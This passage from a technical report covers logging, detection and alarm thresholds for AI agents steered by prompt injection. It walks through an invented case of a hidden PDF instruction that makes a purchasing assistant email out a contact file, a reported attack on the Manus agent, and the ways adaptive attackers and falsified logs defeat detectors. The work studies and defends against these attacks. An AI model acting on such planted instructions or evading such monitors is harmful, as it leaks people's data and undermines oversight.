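The model developer's copy is a poor substitute for the vendor's own log. Ezell and colleagues reported in 2025 that Anthropic kept inputs and outputs for 30 days by default, and for up to two years when it detected a violation of its usage policies. OpenAI and Anthropic also offered approved customers agreements under which the developers stored nothing by default. If a stranger contacts the 120 people a month after the theft, a copy kept for 30 days may already be gone. Ezell and colleagues suggest a default retention period that a company can extend when an investigation begins, with longer periods for riskier uses, such as agents that make purchases through a user's accounts.

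### Who may read it

The logs needed to investigate the theft of 120 people's contact details may themselves contain those details. EU data-protection law requires companies to keep no more personal data than they need for their purpose (data minimisation). The European Commission has proposed amendments to that law, but they were still under negotiation according to White & Case's *EU AI Omnibus enters into force, amending the AI Act* (August 2026). Replacing names with codes gives only partial protection, and Sidhu and colleagues cite research on attacks that work out who the people are.

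A useful compromise is to keep the outside content from every session for a limited period and restrict who can open it. Keeping full text only for sessions that raised an alarm would protect privacy better, but it would delete the evidence in cases that nobody noticed at the time, which may be most of them. Support staff could see the times, tools and identifiers, while an investigator would need to state a reason to read the text, and the system would log each access. The company can then decide separately what to disclose in a report. A later section covers the risks of disclosure.

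The log store also contains planted instructions that still work. If the vendor uses an AI agent to search the logs, the supplier's hidden line could steer that agent too. The searching agent should therefore be unable to send data out or change the records.

### Making tampering evident

An attacker might alter the logs to hide a theft, and a vendor might do so to avoid blame. A hash chain makes later changes visible. Each entry's hash covers the entry itself and the hash of the entry before it:

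hᵢ = H(entryᵢ ‖ hᵢ₋₁)

Here H is the hash function and ‖ means joining the two pieces before hashing them. If someone edits entry 5, its hash no longer matches the one stored in entry 6. A person who controls the whole log could recalculate every later hash, so the vendor should regularly send the latest hash to an outsider, such as the manufacturer. The vendor can still delete personal data if the chain covers only a document's hash, not its text. *NovaFabric* (2026), a proposed system for recording agent runs, adds cryptographic attestation of redactions.

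A hash chain can't show that an entry was true when the software wrote it. In *Hearsay*, Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026) made a coding agent's scaffolding omit a reply from its log in 14 runs and record an invented sentence in another 14. All 28 false records passed the hash-chain check. They also used a language model to read the code of 16 agent frameworks and found none that keeps a record an outsider can check without trusting the software that wrote it.

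Logs can also lose entries by accident. SWE-agent, a widely used coding agent, rejected some of the model's replies, for example because they contained several tool calls at once, and saved neither the replies nor the rejections. This happened in 19 of 28 runs with one model, and the resulting logs looked complete.

People can't reliably spot an altered record by reading it carefully. When Dai and colleagues made one small change to each of 115 records, panels of three people flagged 37% of the altered copies and 10% of the untouched ones. Comparing the log with a second one kept outside the scaffolding worked far better, revealing 64 of 66 alterations in one set of runs with no false alarms on 84 clean records. These were coding tasks in a sandbox where the researchers could observe all the traffic, which is harder to arrange in a business. In the purchasing case, the manufacturer's mail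 server could provide a partial second log, since it might still have an entry for the email if the vendor deleted its own.

### Shared logging formats

OpenTelemetry, an open-source project, publishes common names for log data so that different companies' tools can read it. Its *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* has fields for the conversation, the model, the tool call, its arguments and its result. By default, it leaves out instructions, inputs and outputs because they are often large and sensitive. Recording tool arguments and results is also optional. With the default settings, the purchasing assistant's log could show a call to an email tool but not the recipient or the text of the PDF. For live systems that handle sensitive data, OpenTelemetry recommends keeping the content in a separate store and putting references to it in the log.

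The OpenTelemetry GenAI conventions are still changing. Wang (2026) reports in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* that the project moved them to a separate repository in June 2026, where they were still marked as in development and had no official release as of 21 August. A version history by the software company Greptime (2026) lists changes in each recent release, including a new name for the field that identifies the model's provider. A vendor that adopts the conventions now should record which version it used, so that an investigator can still interpret the fields a year later.

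The OpenTelemetry conventions also leave out much of the information needed to investigate steering. Shah and Kathrotia's list of missing fields includes source labels, the links between content and memory, and the number of times an agent has used an approval. In their tests, a log based on the conventions led to the right step in only 10.8% of faulty runs. A vendor can add these fields to its OpenTelemetry records, but without common names, a manufacturer that uses agents from two vendors would have to match the fields by hand.

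## Methods for detecting a steered agent

A complete log helps only if someone has a reason to open it. In the hypothetical purchasing case, the vendor has no reason to look until a month later, when a stranger writes to the people listed in the stolen file. A detector, which is a program that raises an alarm when a session shows signs of steering, could alert the vendor within seconds.

A detector's hit rate is the share of steered sessions in which it raises an alarm, and its false-alarm rate is the share of unsteered sessions in which it does so. Most detectors give each session a score and raise an alarm when the score is above a threshold, so lowering the threshold increases both rates. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) judges detectors by their hit rate at a 1% false-alarm rate, because an agent reads harmless tool outputs far more often than planted instructions. The next section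 covers how to choose the threshold.

Published tests seldom count whole sessions. Some count tool outputs and others count tasks or attacks, so their figures are only roughly comparable. They also treat awkward cases differently. *BrowseSafe++* (2026), which tests detection on web pages, mostly excludes cases in which a detector refuses to answer or gives an unusable reply, but a live system has to handle them.

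Many tests of detectors use AgentDojo, which simulates a bank, an office, a Slack workspace and a travel service. It has 97 ordinary user tasks and 629 attack cases. Most tests use fixed attacks, which don't adapt to the detector. Attackers who do adapt lower the detector's hit rate, which fell from 98.9% to 74.3% in one condition of *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026).

### Classifiers that read incoming content

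A content classifier scores each tool output before the agent's model receives it. If the score passes a threshold, the scaffolding can stop the session, remove the suspicious passage or send the text to a slower check. Some classifiers are small models trained on examples of attacks. Others, such as PromptArmor, are general language models instructed to look for injections. In PromptArmor, as *MetaPI* (2026) describes it, a guard model looks at each tool output in isolation and quotes any injection it finds, and the program deletes the quoted passage.

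This kind of classifier checks the text without measuring its effect on the agent, so it also flags instructions that the agent would have ignored. It can miss an instruction that reads like a normal business message, as the EchoLeak email did.

In *Prompt-Injection Probes Learn the Conversation, Not Just the Injection*, Kale and Vishwanath (2026) trained a simple text classifier on some AgentDojo applications and tested it on others with fixed attacks. With the threshold set to flag 1% of the new application's normal tool outputs, the classifier caught 87% of the attacks that had fooled the agent. With a threshold carried over from the training applications, it caught only 38%. A vendor that sells the same classifier to a bank and a manufacturer should therefore set the threshold separately for each.

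Off-the-shelf classifiers can do much worse. *MELON* (Zhu, Yang and colleagues, 2025) found that a classifier based on DeBERTa, a small language model, raised a false alarm on 61.86% of AgentDojo's ordinary tasks. GPT-4o in the same role raised none, but both missed at least a fifth of the attacks. *AgentShield* (Rassul and Rashid, 2026) found that two ready-made classifiers flagged nearly everything in Kurdish and Arabic, so a manufacturer with suppliers abroad would need to test in those suppliers' languages.

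Some classifiers add more delay than others. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (Chauhan and Revankar, 2026) reports a credential-theft test in which an input filter added 120 milliseconds, with a hit rate of 60% and a false-alarm rate of 15%. Kale and Vishwanath report that a language model used as a checker takes about a second per item. The vendor also pays for an extra model call each time.

### Readings of the model's internal activations

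Activations are the numbers that a model computes internally as it processes text. *Get my drift?* (2024) introduced a way to detect a change of task from these activations. The detector records them after the model reads the user's request and again after it reads the outside content. A simple classifier, trained on examples with and without injections, then uses the difference between the two sets to detect whether the task has changed.

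Many newer detectors measure the model's activations once, just before it starts its reply. A linear probe multiplies each activation by a learned weight and adds up the results to get a score. This takes little extra computation because the model has already computed the activations. Kale and Vishwanath report that Anthropic runs such probes on tool outputs in many of its products.

Researchers tested their own probes on six open models in AgentDojo with fixed attacks. With the threshold set to flag 1% of normal tool outputs in the training applications, the probes caught a median of 95% of successful attacks in those applications and 82% in new ones.

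They mainly warn about how others train and test probes. They compared each attacked conversation with its clean twin, the same moment in the same task without the injection. At the default threshold, probes trained in the standard way flagged 80% of the clean twins in familiar applications. These probes had partly learned where in a conversation injections tend to occur and how much text surrounds them. A program given only such counts, and no data from the model, scored an AUROC of 0.91 to 0.98 on the standard test. AUROC is the probability that a random attack ranks above a random harmless case, with 0.5 for guessing and 1 for perfect ranking.

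Adding clean twins and harmless lookalikes to the training data cut false alarms on the twins to 17%. Kale and Vishwanath estimate that, at the default threshold and with a one-second check for each alarm, a million tool outputs would need about 88 hours of checking with the standard probe and 21 with theirs.

Activations can also help to distinguish an agent that was steered by an injected instruction from one that only read it. *Are You Reading the Right Thing?* (Gupta and Tembey, 2026) compared five detection methods on 2,000 attacks and 1,000 harmless prompts for each of two models. Attention Tracker measures how far a model's attention shifts away from the user's instruction. On one model, Qwen, it had an AUROC of 0.949 for attacks that succeeded and 0.691 for attacks that failed. PIShield, a probe that detects the presence of an injection, had an AUROC of 0.637 for successful attacks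 and 0.898 for failed ones. An alarm from PIShield is therefore better evidence that the retrieved content contained an instruction, and an alarm from Attention Tracker is better evidence that the instruction had an effect. Some of the attacks were strengthened against the models, but none against the detectors.

The main obstacle to activation-based detection is getting access to the activations. The hypothetical vendor runs its agent on another company's model, so it could use activations only if that company offered the readings as a service. *DriftNet* (2026) avoids this problem by using a detector that reads only the trajectory log. Chauhan and Revankar's activation detector added just 1 millisecond of delay, with an 88% hit rate and 1.5% false alarms, but their prototype doesn't cover credentials passed in the arguments of a tool call, which is how agents often use them.

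### Checks of the action against the request

Once the model proposes a tool call, a detector can ask whether the call serves the user's request. A fixed plan is a poor standard for this, because an agent often has to change course after reading something. Wang, Gu and colleagues (2026), in *ActGuard*, update the expectation at every step:

1. When the agent chooses an action, it also predicts which tools it might need next.
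2. The checker compares the next proposed call with that prediction.
3. If the tool is unexpected, the checker removes passages of retrieved text one at a time and measures how the probability of the call changes.
4. The checker also searches earlier content for the call's arguments, such as an email address, since an attacker can misuse a tool that the agent was expected to use.
5. A language model judges the passages that this search turns up. If it confirms an injection, the program removes the passage and the agent chooses again.

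For step 3, the checker computes a score for each passage s. Leaving out an adjustment for the length of the tools' names, it is

Δ(s) = log [P(proposed tool) / P(proposed tool without s)] − log [P(expected tool) / P(expected tool without s)]

Suppose removing the hidden line lowers the probability of the email tool from 0.6 to 0.1 and raises that of a price-comparison tool from 0.2 to 0.7. The score is about 3.0 (using natural logarithms), and the checker passes the line to the language model because the score is above zero. A small open model can supply the probabilities, so the vendor doesn't need access to the internals of the agent's model.

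Wang and colleagues tested ActGuard, including against adaptive attackers, on AgentDojo and on AgentDyn, which has longer tasks and includes legitimate instructions from third parties. The tests measured how often attacks succeeded and how often the agent finished its task, so they don't give ActGuard's hit rate or false-alarm rate.

*AgentTracer* (2026) compares agents' intentions with their actions in stored logs. It detected an average of 97.34% of attacks in 300 logs from each of two sets of test attacks, AgentDyn and InjecAgent. Some of its tracing errors arose because agents had strayed from the request without any injection. TaskShield, which checks whether an agent stays on task, misses only 2.07% of attacks but also blocks about 30% of legitimate requests, according to figures quoted by Rassul and Rashid.

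These checks are weaker when the user's request is vague. If a buyer tells the assistant to "deal with this offer", many actions seem to fit. A planted instruction can also work through an expected action, for example by changing which supplier the assistant recommends. Each check that uses a language model adds a call and some delay.

### Repeat runs without the user's request

An agent that acts on a planted instruction might take the same action without having seen the user's request. Zhu and colleagues built MELON on this idea. After the agent proposes a tool call, MELON runs the same model again, replacing the user's request with a neutral prompt to summarise all the tool outputs so far and carry out any instructions in them. If both runs propose similar calls, MELON raises an alarm and stops the action.

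MELON also keeps the calls from earlier repeat runs, because the agent may finish part of the user's task before it turns to the planted task. It compares only tool calls, since the wording of the replies may differ even when the actions match. For emails, it compares the recipient but not the message text.

The repeat run must not send the file again. *AgentSentry* (2026), a related method, reuses stored tool results and lets the model propose calls without executing them.

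On AgentDojo, the strongest of four fixed attacks succeeded in 51.03% of cases against an undefended GPT-4o agent and in 0.95% with MELON, which implies that MELON stopped about 98% of the attacks that would have worked. It raised false alarms on nine of the 97 ordinary tasks (9.28%). In all nine, the user had told the agent to follow instructions from an outside source, such as a to-do list on a website. Zhu and colleagues consider these real security risks, but the person handling the alarms would find no attacker. A buyer who asks the assistant to follow a supplier's ordering instructions could cause such an alarm.

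Zhu and colleagues examined 66 attacks that MELON missed across three models. In 48 of them, the effect appeared in the agent's reply, for example as advice to buy something expensive, rather than in a tool call. MELON's repeat run roughly doubles the cost of model calls, but it can run alongside the original, which limits the delay.

### Tracking untrusted data into tool calls

Data tracking labels each piece of content with its origin, such as "outside party", and anything derived from that content keeps the label. Before the agent makes a sensitive tool call, such as sending a payment or an email, a program checks the labels on the data involved and applies a rule. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) traces this approach to older work on controlling the flow of information in computer systems.

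Tracking the influence of retrieved content through a language model is difficult because everything in the model's context can affect its output. If the label on retrieved content spreads to every later action, nearly all of them trigger an alarm. If it spreads only to copied text, the tracker misses cases where a document persuades the agent to make a tool call but supplies none of the words in it.

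*Ghost in the Agent* (2026) compared its own tracker, NeuroTaint, with another tracker, FIDES, on fixed scenarios. In 40 scenarios where untrusted content influenced an action indirectly, NeuroTaint detected the influence in 37 and FIDES in 17. In 140 others where the content had no effect on the action, NeuroTaint raised one false alarm and FIDES raised 94. But NeuroTaint raised a false alarm in all 14 control cases where several sources covered overlapping topics, while FIDES did so in nine. Supplier offers overlap in the same way, so NeuroTaint's low false-alarm rate may not carry over to purchasing.

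Trackers also need access to the arguments of a call. *Retrieval Observability Bounds on Provenance Detection for Agent Memory Poisoning* (2026) used 4,360 harmless sessions to examine a detector that checks only the order of operations. The detector could not distinguish theft from the harmless case of an agent recalling a deadline and emailing its team, because the two sequences differ only in the recipient's address. Even with the address, a tracker shows only that retrieved content influenced the call, not that the call was wrong, since an agent may properly reply to an address it found in a supplier's PDF.

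According to Rassul and Rashid, FIDES requires a vendor to rewrite the agent's planning layer, and another system, CaMeL, reduces the share of tasks completed from 84% to 77%.

### Decoys and approved lists

Besides the decoy data described earlier, a vendor can plant fake tools and addresses that no legitimate task needs, and raise an alarm when an agent uses one. Rassul and Rashid's AgentShield combines three fake tools and five fake credentials with a list of approved values, such as known bank accounts and email domains. It checks every tool call before it runs. Each check takes under 50 milliseconds and requires no extra model calls.

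On AgentDojo tasks with their own attacks, AgentShield raised an alarm in 117 of 129 successful attacks on GPT-4o-mini and in all 125 on GPT-5-mini. The GPT-5-mini figure is hard to reconcile with another part of the paper, where the undefended model carries out none of 512 attacks. The paper seems to use a looser definition of success for the 125 cases.

There were no false alarms in 485 harmless runs, so with 95% confidence the true rate is below 0.79%. But those runs were the same 97 tasks, each repeated five times. In a real purchasing department, a list of approved recipients would raise an alarm for each new supplier until somebody updated the list.

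Rassul and Rashid also tested attackers who knew about the defence. No attacks escaped detection on the two commercial models, though GPT-5-mini refused all of them. On two open models, seven of 41 successful attacks escaped detection.

The approved list raised most of the alerts. On GPT-4o-mini, it raised 120 and the fake tools raised 15. The fake credentials raised none in the standard tests because the agents never opened the files containing them. Chauhan and Revankar's text detector for planted credentials caught only 30% of attacks, with no false alarms and a delay of 2 milliseconds.

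*Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) claims that every call to a decoy tool correctly signals an injection (100% precision). Ghifiardi's experiments in *Optional Traps* (2026) give a reason for doubt, although they studied small models acting as attackers rather than steered assistants. A planted key caught the attacking agent in 19 of 20 sessions. But in a separate trial, a legitimate agent that already had the correct key picked up the planted one, used it and lost its access. Ghifiardi recommends treating such an alarm as strong but inconclusive evidence and choosing a response the operator can reverse, such as a 15-minute suspension.

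### What the purchasing case would trigger

Suppose the buyer had asked the assistant to compare the supplier's offer with current prices. All the entries below are invented.

| Detector | What it could register | When it could miss the case |
|---|---|---|
| Content classifier | The hidden line in the PDF | The line reads like an ordinary business request |
| Activation reading | A shift in the model's internal state after it reads the PDF | The vendor has no access to the activations |
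| Check against the request | An email to an outsider during a price comparison | The buyer's request was vague |
| Repeat run | The same email, proposed without the buyer's request | The line changes only the written recommendation |
| Data tracking | A recipient address taken from the PDF | The vendor has labelled the supplier's files as trusted |
| Decoy record | Nothing, because the line asks for one real file | The assistant never touches the decoy |
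| Approved list | An address that is not on the list | The attacker uses an address on an approved domain |

None of these alarms would prove by itself that the hidden line caused the email.

Chu presents a theorem that a control at one layer of an agent cannot detect an attack confined to another. This is a reason to combine detectors, although the purchasing attack leaves traces in several layers. Combining them can also increase false alarms, since a harmless session can set off any of them. When Chauhan and Revankar added planted credentials and a leakage monitor to their activation detector, the hit rate rose from 88% to 94%, false alarms from 1.5% to 1.8% and the delay from 1 to 16 milliseconds. The vendor could run fast checks on every call and keep the repeat run for emails, payments and deletions.

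### When the alarm comes too late

Manus is an AI agent that users can connect to Gmail. TechRadar's *This popular AI agent could be hacked by a single email* describes a case, reported in October 2026, in which researchers at the security company Salt Labs sent Manus emails with hidden instructions. Manus recognised the first attempts and warned the account's owner. The researchers then sent a disguised instruction that made the agent run their code on its server. Manus warned the owner again, but only after the code had run. Salt Labs reported the flaw through Meta's bug bounty programme, and it has since been fixed.

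Salt Labs demonstrated a vulnerability with harmless code, so there is no known victim. The last test would still count as a success for the detector if any warning counted, even if it came after the action. A test should therefore report how many warnings came before the action, as well as the total.

In the invented log, the assistant reads the PDF at 09:12:31 and sends the email at 09:13:05. A one-second check could run in the 34 seconds between them. An alarm at 09:13:06 would be too late to keep the file inside the company, but the manufacturer could still warn the 120 people that morning instead of a month later. Logging the time of each alarm beside the time of the action would show whether the alarm came before or after it.

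### Blocked actions as near misses

Blocking an action is different from detecting an attack. Rassul and Rashid criticise existing defences for trying to prevent attacks without noticing the ones that get through. A successful block can also leave people unaware of the attack. PromptArmor deletes a suspicious passage and lets the agent carry on, while ActGuard removes the passage and has the agent choose again. In both cases, the user gets a normal answer.

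If a filter blocks a hidden instruction in a supplier's PDF and the vendor doesn't record this near miss, nobody will tell the supplier or check whether other customers received the same file. The same instruction could later reach the assistant through a route without a filter, even though the vendor already had a warning.

The log entry for a block should also include the removed text, the blocked call, and the detector's version and score. The vendor could use the content hash to search for other sessions that read the same file. It should also keep records of false alarms, which it needs to calculate its false-alarm rate.

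The evidence a block provides depends on when it happens. If a classifier removes the hidden line before the model reads it, the vendor has found a planted instruction but doesn't know whether the assistant would have obeyed it. If a repeat run stops the email, the assistant had already chosen to send it, so the incident is a much clearer near miss.

### Google's account of Workspace

*Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) describes how Google protects Gemini in Workspace, its suite of office applications that includes Gmail and Docs. Google collects new attacks from its own human testers, automated testing, outside researchers who receive rewards, and public reports. Staff reproduce each attack, check for duplicates and enter it in a catalogue with an assigned owner. Google then generates variants of the attacks to retrain its classifiers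 and improve the instructions for the language models that act as checkers.

Google's central policy engine controls rules that don't depend on a model's judgement, such as when a user must confirm an action, how the software cleans web addresses and which tools an agent may use in sequence. Google can change these rules faster than it can retrain a model, so it uses them for immediate threats. It measures the improvement from a new defence by running simulated attacks against Workspace applications with the defence on and off.

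This is Google's own account, and outsiders can't verify it. Gavish writes that training has made attacks on Gemini less successful, but gives no hit rate, false-alarm rate or number of attacks blocked in real use. The post's only percentage, a 75% boost to synthetic data generation, concerns the production of test material. Gavish also doesn't say whether Google records blocked attempts as near misses or tells the users whose sessions contained them. Publishing counts of blocked attempts, alongside the results of the tests with and without each defence, would show customers how many attempts the defences meet in practice.

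## Setting alarm thresholds when attacks are rare

A vendor that runs one of these detectors has to decide how high a session's score must be before a person reviews it. If steering is rare, even a small false-alarm rate can produce more false alarms than real cases, while a very high threshold misses real cases. The standard way to analyse this choice is signal detection theory, which engineers developed for electronic signals and researchers in psychology and medicine later adopted.

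### Two overlapping distributions

Swets, Dawes and Monahan (2000), in *Psychological Science Can Improve Diagnostic Decisions*, explain the theory with a test for glaucoma, an eye disease associated with high eye pressure. In their illustration, healthy eyes have pressures from 0 to 40 and diseased eyes from 10 to 50, so a reading of 25 could come from either. A doctor who diagnoses glaucoma at 30 or above will miss some diseased eyes and diagnose the disease in some healthy ones. Lowering the threshold would catch more disease but also cause more false alarms.

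The scores of steered and unsteered sessions overlap. *Decision making from economic and signal detection perspectives* (Lynn, Wormwood and colleagues, 2015) distinguishes sensitivity, which depends on how much the two distributions overlap, from bias, which depends on where the threshold lies. Moving the threshold changes only the bias, so catching more steered sessions without raising more false alarms requires a better detector.

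A receiver operating characteristic (ROC) curve plots the hit rate against the false-alarm rate at every possible threshold. Swets and colleagues give two points on such a curve for breast cancer screening. If doctors follow up every woman whose estimated probability of cancer is at least 5%, they might catch 80% of cancers and raise false alarms for 20% of healthy women. At a threshold of 2%, they would catch 95% of cancers and raise false alarms for 50% of healthy women.

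The area under this curve is the AUROC, the ranking measure from the previous section, which Hanley and McNeil explain in *The Meaning and Use of the Area under a Receiver Operating Characteristic*. It covers every threshold, including many that would flag far too much for a vendor to use, so it can rise even when a detector catches fewer attacks at a low false-alarm rate. In *Passing the Test You Trained On*, when a small detector called Sheltron also received the user's request, its AUROC on AgentDojo rose from 0.86 to 0.91, but its hit rate at a 1% false-alarm rate fell from 20.1% to 9.0%.

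### The threshold with the lowest cost

The best threshold depends on the base rate b (the share of all sessions in which steering occurs) and on the cost of each kind of error. The vendor should raise an alarm at score x when

P(x if steered) / P(x if unsteered) ≥ [(1 − b) / b] × [C(false alarm) / C(miss)]

Here C(false alarm) is how much worse a false alarm is than correctly staying silent, and C(miss) is how much worse a miss is than a hit. *Atomoxetine modulates the relationship between perceptual abilities and response bias*, a study of decision-making in monkeys, gives an equivalent formula for the right-hand side and credits it to Tanner and Swets.

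Suppose 10 of the invented vendor's million daily sessions are steered, so b is 1 in 100,000. If both errors cost the same, the vendor should raise an alarm only at scores at least about 100,000 times as likely in a steered session as in an unsteered one. But if a false alarm costs €10 of a reviewer's time and a miss costs €100,000, the required ratio falls to about 10. A session at that threshold has a 1 in 10,000 chance of being steered, but it is still worth checking because 10,000 checks cost as much as one miss.

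The formula gives every false alarm the same weight, which is wrong when reviewers have more alarms than they can read. The vendor pays for the reviews, but much of the damage from a missed attack falls on the manufacturer and the 120 people in the file, so a vendor that counts only its own costs will set the threshold too high. A vendor can also set several thresholds, which Swets and colleagues mention as an option when more than one response is available. For example, a moderate score might lead the agent to ask the buyer for confirmation, and a high score might stop the email.

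### Why most alarms are false

Precision, the share of alarms that are correct, follows from the hit rate h, the false-alarm rate f and the base rate:

precision = b × h / [b × h + (1 − b) × f]

The table applies this to the vendor's million sessions. All the rates are invented.

| Detector | Steered sessions flagged | Unsteered sessions flagged | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 90% hit rate, 0.1% false-alarm rate | 9 | 1,000 | 0.9% |
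| 90% hit rate, 0.001% false-alarm rate | 9 | 10 | 47% |
| The first detector, then a second check with independent errors | 8.55 | 10 | 46% |
| The first detector, then a second check that repeats 30% of its false alarms | 8.55 | 300 | 2.8% |

Only 9 of the first detector's roughly 1,009 alarms are correct, even though the detector sounds accurate. Cutting its false-alarm rate to a hundredth of the current level raises precision to about 47%, while raising the hit rate from 90% to 100% would add only one correct alarm. The vendor can't get from the first row to the second just by raising the threshold, because a stricter threshold would also catch fewer steered sessions.

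Axelsson (2000), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, made the same calculation for conventional computer security. He imagined a small network that produces a million log records a day, 20 of them from intrusions. Even a detector that caught every intrusion would need a false-alarm rate of about 0.001% for two-thirds of its alarms to be correct. Axelsson found no experiments on how many false alarms security staff tolerate, but studies of power stations and factories suggested that most operators lose faith in a device well before half its alarms are false. He also repeated old advice to intruders to try an alarm system during working hours, when the staff are used to false alarms.

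Injection detectors have the same problem. In *PIDS-Bench*, Shire and Kim (2026) trained a detector whose F1 score, which combines precision and hit rate, was above 0.98. Its precision was 89.3% when one input in ten was an attack and 7.0% when one in a thousand was. At the vendor's base rate, the same calculation gives a precision below 0.1%. Shire and Kim tested single English prompts, so the exact figures wouldn't carry over to whole sessions.

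A session can contain many tool outputs, any of which could set off the detector. In *Passing the Test You Trained On*, a detector that flagged 30.1% of harmless tool outputs on AgentDojo would have interrupted 69.1% of the tasks. If each of the purchasing assistant's sessions had 20 tool outputs and the detector flagged 0.1% of harmless ones, it would raise a false alarm in about 2% of sessions, or 20,000 a day.

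Published tests are also too small to confirm the false-alarm rates a vendor needs. Meta's Prompt Guard 2 flagged none of 1,533 harmless outputs from τ-bench, a simulation of customer service, but this only shows with 95% confidence that the true rate is below about 0.2%. The vendor can measure the rate much more precisely from its own traffic. Nearly all its sessions are unsteered, so the share that raises an alarm is almost exactly the false-alarm rate.

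### A second check on the alarms

The vendor could send the first detector's 1,009 alarms to a slower second check that catches 95% of steered sessions and flags 1% of unsteered ones. If their errors are independent, 8.55 correct alarms and 10 false ones remain on an average day (third row of the table). Independence means that an unsteered session flagged by the first detector is no more likely than other unsteered sessions to be flagged by the second check.

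This is unlikely if both detectors look for suspicious wording. In *Prompt Injection Detection for Email Agents Through Attack Chain Modeling* (2026), 30% of a sample of false alarms came from harmless technical instructions and 26% from discussion of security or platforms. *Securing AI Agents Against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025) reports that most false alarms came from ordinary text that resembled instructions, such as technical documentation. A supplier's installation manual could fool both of the vendor's detectors for the same reason. If the second detector also flagged 30% of the first detector's false alarms, 300 would remain and precision would be 2.8%.

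Raising the threshold wouldn't remove many of these errors. Shire and Kim gave their best detector 1,472 harmless prompts that resembled attacks or concerned security, and in one training run it scored 32.1% of them at 0.9 or higher out of 1. They then retrained it with 419 extra harmless examples. False alarms fell from 48.1% to 0.1% on prompts similar to the new examples, but only from 31.4% to 31.0% on prompts from public collections. The vendor's own false alarms might make better training examples, though Shire and Kim didn't test examples matched to the text a detector will process.

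A second check that uses different evidence should help more. If the first detector reads the PDF, the second check could assess whether sending the file serves the buyer's request. The vendor should measure the second check's false-alarm rate on sessions that the first detector wrongly flagged, since the rate on ordinary sessions could be much lower.

### Grouping alarms by source

*Intrusion-Detection Policies for IT Security Breaches* notes that acting on every alarm is wasteful when few are correct, but ignoring alarms makes the detector useless. It proposes policies of waiting before responding. An AI agent's vendor can use that time to check whether several alarms come from the same document.

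Suppose 200 sessions a day read the same supplier's PDF. At a false-alarm rate of 0.1%, they should produce an average of 0.2 false alarms a day. If false alarms occur independently, the chance of five or more in a day is about 2 in a million. With 5,000 documents, each read in 200 sessions a day, some document would reach five false alarms in a day about once every 90 days. If a planted instruction steered ten of a document's 200 sessions and the detector caught each with 90% probability, that document would almost certainly reach five alarms.

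The independence assumption can also fail badly here. A content classifier that gives an installation manual a high score in one session will give it the same score in the other 199. The average false-alarm rate of 0.1% could come from five harmless documents that are flagged in every session, and each would exceed the limit of five alarms every day. The calculation suits detectors whose errors depend on the session, such as those that check the agent's action against the user's request.

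Grouping would still save work in that case, because a reviewer could dismiss 1,000 false alarms by reading five documents. The vendor should store the verdict with the document's content hash and reopen the case if the text changes. It should also keep checking the agent's actions after a reviewer clears a document, since the reviewer may have missed a hidden line.

An attacker can defeat grouping by content hash by making every copy slightly different. The vendor could also group alarms by sender, web domain or the address the agent sent data to. Each extra grouping gives unrelated alarms another way to match by chance, so the vendor has to raise the limit to keep chance signals equally rare. Grouping does little against a targeted attack, because if only one session reads the supplier's PDF, there is no second alarm to add to the first.

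### Slow changes

A few extra alarms a day at one customer may never pass a daily limit. Cumulative-sum monitoring, a method from industrial quality control, adds up small excesses over time. Each day, the vendor updates a running total:

Sₜ = max(0, Sₜ₋₁ + xₜ − k)

Here xₜ is the number of alarms on day t, and k is a reference value slightly above the normal average. The vendor investigates when S passes a limit.

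Suppose a customer normally has 20 false alarms a day, and the vendor sets k at 22. Counts of 25, 23, 21 and 26 on four days would take the total from zero to 3, 4, 3 and 7. In normal times the total keeps falling back to zero. If steering adds four alarms a day, the average count rises to 24. A count of 24 on any single day is unremarkable because chance alone often moves the count by four or five, but the total now grows by about two a day and passes a limit of 22 after about eleven days.

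With a lower limit, the vendor would detect the change sooner but get more false alarms. At a limit of 22, this customer's total would pass the limit by chance roughly once a year, so a vendor with 50 such customers would get a false alarm about once a week. A new version of the detector or a new type of document can also raise the total. The vendor should recalculate the normal average after each update and compare customers who received the update at the same time.

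This method can't reveal attacks that raise no alarms. To look for those, the vendor could apply the same formula to other counts, such as the number of emails its agents send to new recipients.

### Finding out what the detector misses

Applying Axelsson's calculation to sessions without an alarm gives a misleading result because steering is so rare. With one missed case among the vendor's 999,000 unflagged sessions, an unflagged session has a more than 99.999% chance of being harmless. But a detector that never raised an alarm would also achieve 99.999%. To learn the miss rate, the vendor has to look for steered sessions among the unflagged ones.

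If reviewers examine n random unflagged sessions and find no steering, they can be 95% confident that the rate of steering among unflagged sessions is below about 3/n. An audit of 300,000 sessions that finds none therefore limits the missed rate to about 1 in 100,000, or ten cases a day if there are a million unflagged sessions daily. If the detector catches nine cases a day and misses as many as ten, its hit rate could be as low as 47%.

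The limit also assumes that reviewers would recognise a case. If they recognise only half, it doubles to 1 in 50,000. Reviewers also have a threshold for flagging a session, and *Beyond detection rate* uses signal detection theory to study how people's performance declines when they have to stay vigilant. Someone who has read thousands of harmless logs may skim past the hidden line. At one minute per session, the audit would take 5,000 hours, so the vendor would probably have to use a slow automated check, such as a repeat run without the user's request, and pass only suspicious sessions to people. Reviewers would then never see the cases that the check failed to flag.

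Targeted sampling reduces the number of sessions that need review. Suppose the detector misses ten cases a day, and eight of them are among the 20,000 unflagged sessions in which an agent read outside content and then sent data to a new address. Reviewing 7,500 sessions from that group would give at least a 95% chance of finding a case, compared with 300,000 from the whole population. The vendor still needs a random sample of the other sessions, where the agent may have recommended the wrong supplier without sending anything. To estimate the total, the vendor should weight each case by the inverse of its group's sampling rate, so a case from a group sampled at 1 in 1,000 counts as about 1,000 cases.

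Reviewing only sessions that scored just below the threshold would miss real attacks to which the detector gave a low attack probability. *Confidently Wrong* (2026) studies such attacks, which the system relying on the detector then treats as safe.

### Seeded test cases

The vendor can also plant its own test instructions, for example in copies of supplier PDFs that a test version of the assistant reads, and count how many the detector catches. If it catches 90 of 100, its hit rate on such cases is between about 82% and 95%, with 95% confidence. Adding sessions with planted instructions to the audit queue would test the reviewers in the same way. If they recognised 80% of the planted cases, an audit of 300,000 sessions that found no real attacks would put the upper limit on the rate of missed attacks at about 1 in 80,000 sessions.

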